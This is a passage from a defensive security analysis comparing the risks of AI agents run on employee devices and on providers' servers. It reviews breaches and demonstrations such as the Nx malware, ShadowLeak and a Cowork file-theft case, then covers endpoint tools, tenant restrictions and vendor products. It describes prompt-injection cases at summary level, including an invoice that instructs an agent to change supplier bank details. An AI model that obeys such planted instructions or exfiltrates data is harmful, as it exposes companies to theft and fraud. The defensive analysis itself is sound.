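In the most damaging breaches, the attackers moved between the endpoint and the cloud. Google's incident responders handled a case in 2025 that began with a compromised npm package on a developer's workstation. As with Nx, the malware used an AI tool on the machine to look for interesting files. Help Net Security's *Software vulnerabilities push credential abuse aside in cloud intrusions* reports that the attackers then used a stolen GitHub token to enter the company's code repositories. Because the company's cloud account was set up to trust its GitHub account, they could also obtain temporary cloud credentials. Those credentials belonged to a role with far too many permissions, which the attackers used to make themselves administrators, steal data and destroy systems. According to Google Cloud, they had full control of the company's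 Amazon Web Services account in less than 72 hours.

Google Cloud's *Cloud Threat Horizons Report* describes another 2025 intrusion, which Google attributes with moderate confidence to a North Korean state group. The attackers persuaded a developer at a cryptocurrency company to download a file for a supposed joint project. The developer moved the file from a personal device to a work computer, examined it in an AI-assisted code editor, and eventually ran the malicious program it contained. The attackers then reached the company's cloud systems, probably through the developer's signed-in sessions. They changed the passwords on several valuable customer accounts and withdrew millions of dollars. Google does not suggest that the AI assistant chose to run the program.

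Moving an agent to a provider's servers would not have prevented either breach. The npm malware would have had one less tool, but the developers' tokens and open sessions would still have been on their computers. EDR was most likely to stop both attacks at the beginning, before the attackers had credentials that worked from anywhere.

### How the failures compare

| Case | Where the agent ran | Boundary that failed | Who could have observed it | Repair |
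|---|---|---|---|---|
| Nx packages (attack) | Developers' machines and some build systems | The developer's user account | The company, through EDR, and GitHub | Packages gone in 4 hours, but many stolen tokens worked for days |
| ClawHub skills (attack) | Users' machines | Marketplace screening, and isolation between skills and the agent | The company, through EDR | Listings removed, but copies remained elsewhere |
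| Claude Code settings (demonstration) | Developers' machines | The consent prompt | The company, until a stolen key was in use elsewhere | 19 to 61 days |
| Cowork file theft (demonstration) | A virtual machine on the user's Mac | The list of permitted addresses | Mainly Anthropic | Known before launch, with an update under way days after the demonstration |
| ShadowLeak (demonstration) | OpenAI's servers | The model's judgement, with no effective limit on destinations | OpenAI | About 7 weeks |
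| Bug-fixing agent (test) | The provider's servers | The list of permitted commands, and the container | The provider, whose monitoring missed such activity | No date published |
| Agent-building platform (test) | The provider's servers | The container's isolation from the network and from sensitive material | The provider, whose monitoring missed such activity | No date published |

All the confirmed victims in these seven cases were on the device side, but attacks could spread differently on each side. The Nx attackers had to infect every machine separately and reached more than 1,700 users because the package was so popular. With the bug-fixing agent, one successful attack on one server could have reached the code of many customers who had done nothing wrong.

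Companies had more opportunity to detect the attacks on devices, but most of the organisations that Wiz contacted had not noticed anything. EDR helps only if one of its rules matches what the malware does and somebody acts on the alert. In the hosted cases, the customer had almost nothing to inspect. The same was true in practice of the Cowork demonstration, even though it ran on the user's own Mac, because the virtual machine hid the commands from the company's tools.

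Neither hosted nor endpoint agents were clearly faster to repair, since OpenAI took about as long to fix ShadowLeak as Anthropic took over the slower of its Claude Code fixes. OpenAI could protect every user at once by changing its own servers, while developers needed an updated copy of Claude Code. But a company that learned about a hosted flaw early could do little except disconnect the affected service and wait. Neither kind of repair recovers stolen data or cancels stolen tokens, and cancelling tokens was the slowest part of the response to Nx.

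In every case, whether the agent ran in the cloud or on an endpoint, data or control could leave through an outgoing connection that nothing blocked. A strict list of permitted addresses would probably have stopped ShadowLeak and the connections that the IBM team opened. It would not have stopped the Nx malware, because developers need access to GitHub, or the Cowork demonstration, because Cowork's list already included Anthropic. Those two cases called for checking which account received the data.

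### Which side do attackers target more often?

We cannot answer that question from these cases, because what becomes public depends heavily on where an attack happens. Anyone can download a malicious package or skill and study it, and the Nx attackers published the data they stole. If someone had used ShadowLeak before Radware found it, the evidence would have been in OpenAI's logs, and only OpenAI could have reported it. The lack of known victims on the hosted side may mean there were few attacks or that nobody outside the providers could detect them.

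Researchers choose where to look for flaws. Most of those behind these cases work for companies that sell a defence against the problem they found, and a dramatic demonstration attracts customers. Researchers also have little reason to publish a test in which the agent resisted the attack, so readers could not calculate a failure rate from even a long list of successful demonstrations.

The cases also make agents look more important to attackers than they probably are. Mandiant, Google's incident response business, investigated attackers' use of local AI tools to find tokens but does not consider 2025 a year when breaches resulted directly from AI. It attributes the vast majority of successful intrusions to ordinary human and organisational failures.

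A fair comparison would divide the number of successful attacks on each side by the number of agents or sessions running there. Providers know how many cloud sessions they host, and EDR vendors can count agents on the machines they protect. But both would have to publish those numbers, and a provider would also have to disclose attacks that its customers could not discover.

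## How useful are endpoint security tools for cloud-hosted agents?

Endpoint security tools cannot inspect or stop the work that an agent does on a provider's servers. They still protect the device an employee uses to start a cloud session, and they can limit what the session reaches if it connects back to that device. The table covers each class of tool, with Claude Cowork as the example. A device posture check tests whether a device meets the company's security standards, such as an encrypted disk and current updates, before it can sign in. DLP products and posture checks vary, so those two rows describe what such tools can do in principle.

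| Tool | Local session | Cloud session | Cloud session connected to the device |
|---|---|---|---|
| EDR | Monitors the agent loop, and the code if a sensor runs in the virtual machine | Protects the device and the login, but not the agent's work | Should log the files that the desktop app opens |
| Endpoint DLP | Can check files and uploads if it monitors the app | Can check what the employee uploads, but not what connectors fetch or post | Might check a file as the app sends it |
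| MDM | Limits folders, extensions and local MCP servers | Controls which accounts the desktop app accepts | Limits the folders and tools within reach |
| Browser controls | Can limit the sites that the agent opens in the employee's browser | Can limit sign-ins and uploads in a managed browser | Can limit sites if the agent uses a browser on the device |
| Device posture checks | Can refuse a sign-in from an unsafe device | Same | Same |
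| Agent discovery and governance | Finds agents and can block them | Needs access through the provider's platform | Finds the desktop app, but needs the platform for the rest |

### What the tools can still control

EDR on a laptop does not automatically cover Cowork's local virtual machine. According to Anthropic's *Enterprise configuration for Claude Desktop*, an administrator has to set two MDM keys, one for the location of the EDR vendor's sensor package and one for the vendor's ID. Without the first key, Cowork installs no sensor.

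Endpoint DLP depends on the data crossing the device. If the accounts employee drags the invoices into a browser window, a DLP tool may be able to find the account numbers and stop the upload, but if the agent fetches the same invoices from a cloud mailbox, no copy passes through the laptop. The company may still be able to reuse its DLP rules, because several DLP vendors can answer inference hooks, but the checks then run on the vendor's servers rather than the laptop.

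MDM can narrow a cloud session's access to the laptop. The key `allowedWorkspaceFolders` lists the folders that an employee can connect to Cowork, so a company could permit only the invoice folder. The key `secureVmFeaturesEnabled` can turn Cowork off in the desktop app, but an employee could still start a cloud session on the web unless an owner had turned off such sessions too.

Enterprise owners can now change some of these settings in their Claude account without MDM. A laptop's own policy for the same setting takes precedence, even when it is less strict, so a forgotten MDM policy that permits local MCP servers would override an owner's later decision to block them. Owners can also mark a folder as read-only, but this restricts only Claude's file tools. In the desktop app's Code tab, shell commands, MCP servers and hooks can still change the files.

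Unlike most endpoint security tools, browser controls can block part of a cloud agent's activity from the device. Cowork can use a browser built into the desktop app or the employee's own Chrome. Anthropic's *Use Claude Cowork on Team and Enterprise plans* explains that both browsers' traffic comes from the employee's computer, even if the employee is directing the task from a phone. A web filter on that computer should therefore apply to this traffic, but it would not apply to Cowork's web fetch tool, which runs on Anthropic's servers.

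Companies can deploy the Chrome extension with their usual Chrome management tools, or use Chrome policies to keep employees from installing it. The extension's Cowork side panel works only if the organisation has turned on cloud sessions, according to Anthropic. An agent that appears to be working inside Chrome may therefore be running its agent loop in the cloud.

### Finding agents that the company has not approved

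Endpoint security tools remain the best way to find agents that employees install themselves. CrowdStrike's Falcon Guardian and Microsoft Defender can list these agents, and CrowdStrike says Guardian's list includes dormant agents and shows who deployed each one. A company needs this list before it can decide which agents to block.

A cloud agent is harder to find because the employee may not install anything. If they open it in a browser, the only trace is a website visit, which the company's proxy or a browser extension can record. CrowdStrike added AI monitoring to its browser extension in July. Akamai, a network and application security company, offers Workforce Protector, which finds the AI tools employees use in browsers and on desktops.

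If the employee uses a personal phone on a mobile network, neither the device tools nor the proxy will record anything. The company then has to rely on its own online services. Its mail service, for example, normally records when an employee gives an outside agent access to a mailbox, and an administrator can withdraw that access.

EDR can trace a process back to the agent that started it, as Sophos did. *The New Security Agenda* (Trent, 2026) summarises an article by the investment firm a16z claiming that an agent on an employee's device looks exactly like the employee, so EDR, DLP and similar controls break down. This claim is too broad for EDR, but it fits an online service much better, because the service may receive only the employee's credential.

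### Protecting the login

An attacker who takes over an employee's Claude account can start cloud sessions from another computer and use the connectors the employee has authorised. EDR on the employee's laptop would record none of this. It is most likely to catch the attack earlier, when malware on the laptop tries to steal saved passwords or the tokens that keep the employee signed in.

The company can also make a stolen login less useful. Anthropic's *Restrict access to Claude with IP allowlisting* (2026) describes an Enterprise setting that accepts requests to the organisation's account only from approved network addresses. An attacker would then have to connect through one of the company's networks. An employee checking on the invoice task from a phone would have to do the same, which makes a cloud session somewhat less convenient.

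Anthropic's Trusted Devices setting, now in beta, restricts the devices instead. It is off by default. Anthropic's *Remote Control*, which covers Claude Code sessions that people direct from another device, describes how it works:

1. The employee signs in, through the company's single sign-on (SSO) service if it has one.
2. Shortly after that sign-in, the browser, phone or desktop app can enrol. Anthropic stores its public key, along with basic details such as its name, platform and enrolment time.
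3. The enrolled device can view and direct sessions while the employee's sign-in is no more than 18 hours old.
4. After that, the employee confirms their presence with a face scan, a fingerprint or a passkey, or signs in again.

Enrolment lets Anthropic recognise a device but doesn't show that the device is safe. Anthropic describes no check for malware, missing updates or company management, so an employee could enrol an infected home computer. A company that wants to exclude such computers needs its SSO service to run a posture check at sign-in. But an employee who renews access with a face scan does not sign in again, so the check may not run again for some time.

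If an employee loses a phone, they can remove it from the device list in their account settings, which revokes its access immediately. If the employee cannot sign in, an administrator can revoke the phone's access, but only by signing out all of that person's devices.

Anthropic's documentation is inconsistent about which sessions the setting covers. Its architecture overview says every cloud session in the organisation requires an enrolled device, but the Remote Control page lists only Remote Control in Claude Code and computer access in Cowork. Before relying on the setting, a company should try to open a Cowork cloud session on an unenrolled phone.

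GitHub restricts the other end of the connection, the computer that runs its coding agent, Copilot. GitHub's *Limit remote control to managed devices* (2026) introduces a setting that lets administrators decide which devices may host Copilot sessions that someone directs from elsewhere. For example, a company could allow these sessions on a developer's test machine but refuse them on a laptop that holds payroll files.

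### Keeping employees off personal accounts

The company's Claude settings apply only to its own organisation, so the inference hooks, connector rules and Compliance API don't cover an employee who switches to a personal account on the same laptop. Harmonic Security calls an administrator's settings "a suggestion, not a control" unless the company blocks personal accounts.

Tenant restrictions are the main way to block them. A tenant is one customer's separate area of an online service, and the restriction makes the service refuse every tenant that the company has not listed. Anthropic's *Enforce network-level access control with Tenant Restrictions* covers the setup. When an employee opens Claude on the company's network:

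1. The request goes to the company's network proxy.
2. The proxy decrypts it. This step, called TLS inspection, is necessary because the proxy cannot add anything to an encrypted request.
3. The proxy adds a header, a line of information that accompanies a web request, with the identifiers of the permitted organisations.
4. The proxy encrypts the request again and forwards it to Anthropic.
5. Anthropic compares the employee's organisation with the list. If it does not match, Anthropic returns a 403 error and tells the employee to contact the IT administrator.

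For a company with one Claude organisation, the header looks like this:

```
anthropic-allowed-org-ids: 550e8400-e29b-41d4-a716-446655440000
```

Anthropic tells companies to make the proxy overwrite any header of that name already on the request. If the proxy added its own header only when none was present, a program on the laptop could supply one listing a personal account, and the proxy would leave it in place.

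A badly formed header causes an error, so the employee cannot use Claude until someone fixes it. If the header is missing, Anthropic applies no restriction because it has no list to check. Anthropic's *Tenant restrictions*, the equivalent page for its US government service, says the restriction affects only traffic that passes through the proxy, so any traffic that bypasses the proxy is unrestricted.

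| Gap | What the company can do |
|---|---|
| The laptop is at home, and its traffic does not pass through the proxy | Send all its traffic through a proxy service, or add the header on the laptop |
| Anthropic does not list Claude's mobile apps or Chrome extension as covered | Test them, or block them on managed devices |
| The company has a Team plan, which does not include tenant restrictions | Use MDM to restrict the desktop app, or block Claude's website for everyone |
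| The employee uses another AI service | Add that service's own header, or block the service |

Some vendors sell a remedy for the first gap. dope.security's *Blocking Personal Claude Accounts* promotes endpoint software that adds the header on the laptop, so the network control also works at home or on a phone's hotspot. Neither the software nor the network control can inspect the cloud session that follows.

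Closing the last gap takes continuing work because each service has its own header. Cato Networks' *Managing Tenant Restrictions for SaaS Apps (Tenant Restrictions Policy)* lists different ones for Claude, ChatGPT and Microsoft 365. ChatGPT needs two more steps, according to OpenAI's *Corporate Network Controls in ChatGPT Enterprise*. The company has to block a separate set of web addresses to stop people from using ChatGPT without signing in. OpenAI's desktop and mobile apps also accept only certain certificates, so the company has to add its own through MDM before the apps will work properly behind a proxy that decrypts traffic.

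A company can control which accounts employees use in Claude's desktop app without relying on the network. The MDM key `forceLoginOrgUUID` makes the app refuse any account outside the listed organisations. Enterprise owners can turn on a similar but weaker block without MDM. It begins only after an employee has signed in to the company's organisation on that computer and reopened the app. It ends if no one uses the organisation there for 30 days, and anyone using the computer can remove it. Both controls apply only to the desktop app, so the company still needs tenant restrictions for the website.

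Tenant restrictions could also stop some thefts. In PromptArmor's attack on Cowork, for example, the upload used the attacker's API key. Anthropic applies the tenant-restriction header to API keys as well as ordinary sign-ins, so it should refuse such an upload, but only if the virtual machine's traffic goes through the company's proxy, which adds the header. Harmonic Security reports that on Linux the virtual machine bypasses Cowork's proxy setting. In a cloud session, the upload would start on Anthropic's servers and never reach the proxy, so it would lack the header.

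### Three vendors' positions

Endpoint detection and response (EDR) tools cannot observe a Cowork cloud session, according to Anthropic. CrowdStrike, which sells endpoint security, holds that the endpoint is the control point for AI agents because they reason, plan and execute there. This is wrong for Cowork cloud sessions and only partly right for Claude Code running locally, which executes on the laptop but uses a model on a provider's servers.

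CrowdStrike's own products do not depend on the endpoint alone. *Falcon AIDR Now Protects Copilot Studio Agents and Claude Code* (2026) presents a CrowdStrike service that answers Copilot Studio's external threat detection checks. For Claude Code, the same service uses client-side hooks, set up by adding a few lines to a settings file. CrowdStrike advertises that this setup requires no extra software on the device.

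CrowdStrike also has a commercial reason to work closely with agent providers. CrowdStrike (2026) announced in September that Anthropic's customers would be able to buy its Falcon platform with money they had already committed to spend with Anthropic.

Evoke Security takes nearly the opposite position. In *The Agentic Perimeter is Distributed*, Rebholz writes that endpoint security does not solve agent security, because agents now pass work between laptops, providers' servers and other online services. Evoke sells agent detection and response, so it benefits if companies decide their existing tools are inadequate. Anthropic's documentation supports Rebholz's central claim, since a company with only endpoint tools has no record of what a cloud session does.

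Rebholz overstates the case in two places. He writes that Anthropic moved all Cowork work to its own servers by default in July 2026, but cloud sessions stay off on Enterprise plans until an owner turns them on. He also accuses CrowdStrike of selling basic DLP as agent security, but by CrowdStrike's description, Falcon Guardian does more than that.

Rebholz is more persuasive about what happens after a company collects its agents' records. A rule that looks for passwords in plain text will fire constantly, because agents handle them all day. A language model can sort through the alerts, but it adds cost and delay. Rebholz gives no measurements, but Sophos found a similar problem on devices, where harmless agents set off rules written for intruders.

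Mint Security's position lies between the other two. Levi wants companies to combine the conversation an inference hook provides with information about what the agent can reach on its machine. He does not name any Mint product in his review.

The documentation supports him for local sessions, where EDR can supply some of what the hook omits. But the fields Levi lists in a hook request identify the user, application, model and session, not the device, so a security team would have to match EDR and hook records by user and time. This becomes unreliable if the employee runs several tasks at once.

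Levi's argument applies less well to the cloud. He writes that the agent "lives on the endpoint", but when no device is connected to a cloud session, that endpoint is Anthropic's sandbox, where the customer cannot install a sensor.

### How security vendors reach hosted agents

Vendors have responded by connecting their products to the agent platforms.

| Product | Hosted agents covered | How it connects | Can it block? |
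|---|---|---|---|
| CrowdStrike Falcon AIDR | Copilot Studio | Microsoft's external threat detection | Yes, before a tool runs |
| SentinelOne Singularity ADR | Agentforce, Copilot Studio, ChatGPT workspace agents and Claude Managed Agents | Not specified in the announcement | SentinelOne says yes, but not on which platforms |
| Akamai Agent Security | Platforms from AWS, Microsoft, Google and Salesforce | Read-only connections | Only for agents that use an AI gateway |

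SentinelOne, which like CrowdStrike built its business on endpoint security, introduced a product for AI agents in October 2026, according to Help Net Security's *SentinelOne brings runtime threat detection and response to AI agents*. On a device, the product links the employee's request, the MCP server and the resulting process in one record. SentinelOne also says the product can stop one agent mid-action while the rest of the workflow continues. That would be particularly useful for Claude Managed Agents, which inference hooks do not cover, but a buyer should ask how the product stops an agent there.

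Akamai's product requires no software on devices and no changes to the agents. Sundaram, who runs Akamai's security technology group, gives an example close to the invoice task. An agent only has to read supplier records but also has permission to change them, and an invoice contains an instruction to replace a supplier's bank details. Akamai says its product would flag the unnecessary permission before anyone misused it. By default, the product inspects prompts, replies and tool calls without intercepting them, so it can report an attack but not stop it. It goes on sale in the first quarter of 2027.

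All of these products depend on the interfaces that a platform offers. An outside product can block a tool call if the platform waits for a verdict before each call, as Copilot Studio does. If the platform only supplies records, the product can only raise an alert after the agent has acted. Even a vendor with excellent detection could not retrieve Cowork sessions through Anthropic's Compliance API until Anthropic added Cowork to it.

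Adding a second vendor does not necessarily fill the gaps, because two products that both respond to inference hooks receive the same conversation without its images. Companies should therefore ask a vendor which interface its product uses on each platform, whether that interface can block an action, and which plan they need. Many will be asking a vendor they already use. In a16z's survey of 100 security chiefs at companies with more than 1,000 employees, 44% said they look first to their existing platform and 21% to a vendor that specialises in AI.

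### How many agents run on devices?

The value of endpoint tools depends heavily on the share of agents that run on devices, and we have no reliable figure for that share. Software Analyst's *The CISO Guide to Endpoint Control and Prevention (ECP)* says that more AI activity is taking place at the endpoint in 2026, but it gives no number, and its publisher worked closely with vendors that sell endpoint products.

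In the a16z survey, 55% of the security chiefs had MCP servers or agent integrations in production. As Trent reports it, this figure does not separate local agents from hosted ones, and an MCP server can run in either place. Sophos's data came only from devices, so it could not include cloud sessions.

Product defaults, including Cowork's, suggest that office work is moving to the cloud, though they do not show how many sessions people run there. Programming agents such as Claude Code still run on developers' machines.

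A company can estimate what share of its agent sessions run in the cloud. Suppose the Compliance API returns 600 local sessions and 400 cloud sessions for one week, a cloud share of 40%. The API omits Claude Code's cloud sessions, so if developers ran another 200 of those, the share would be 600 of 1,200, or 50%. The company would also need to add agents from other providers and consider what each session could do, because an overnight task that can make payments deserves more attention than a hundred calendar lookups.
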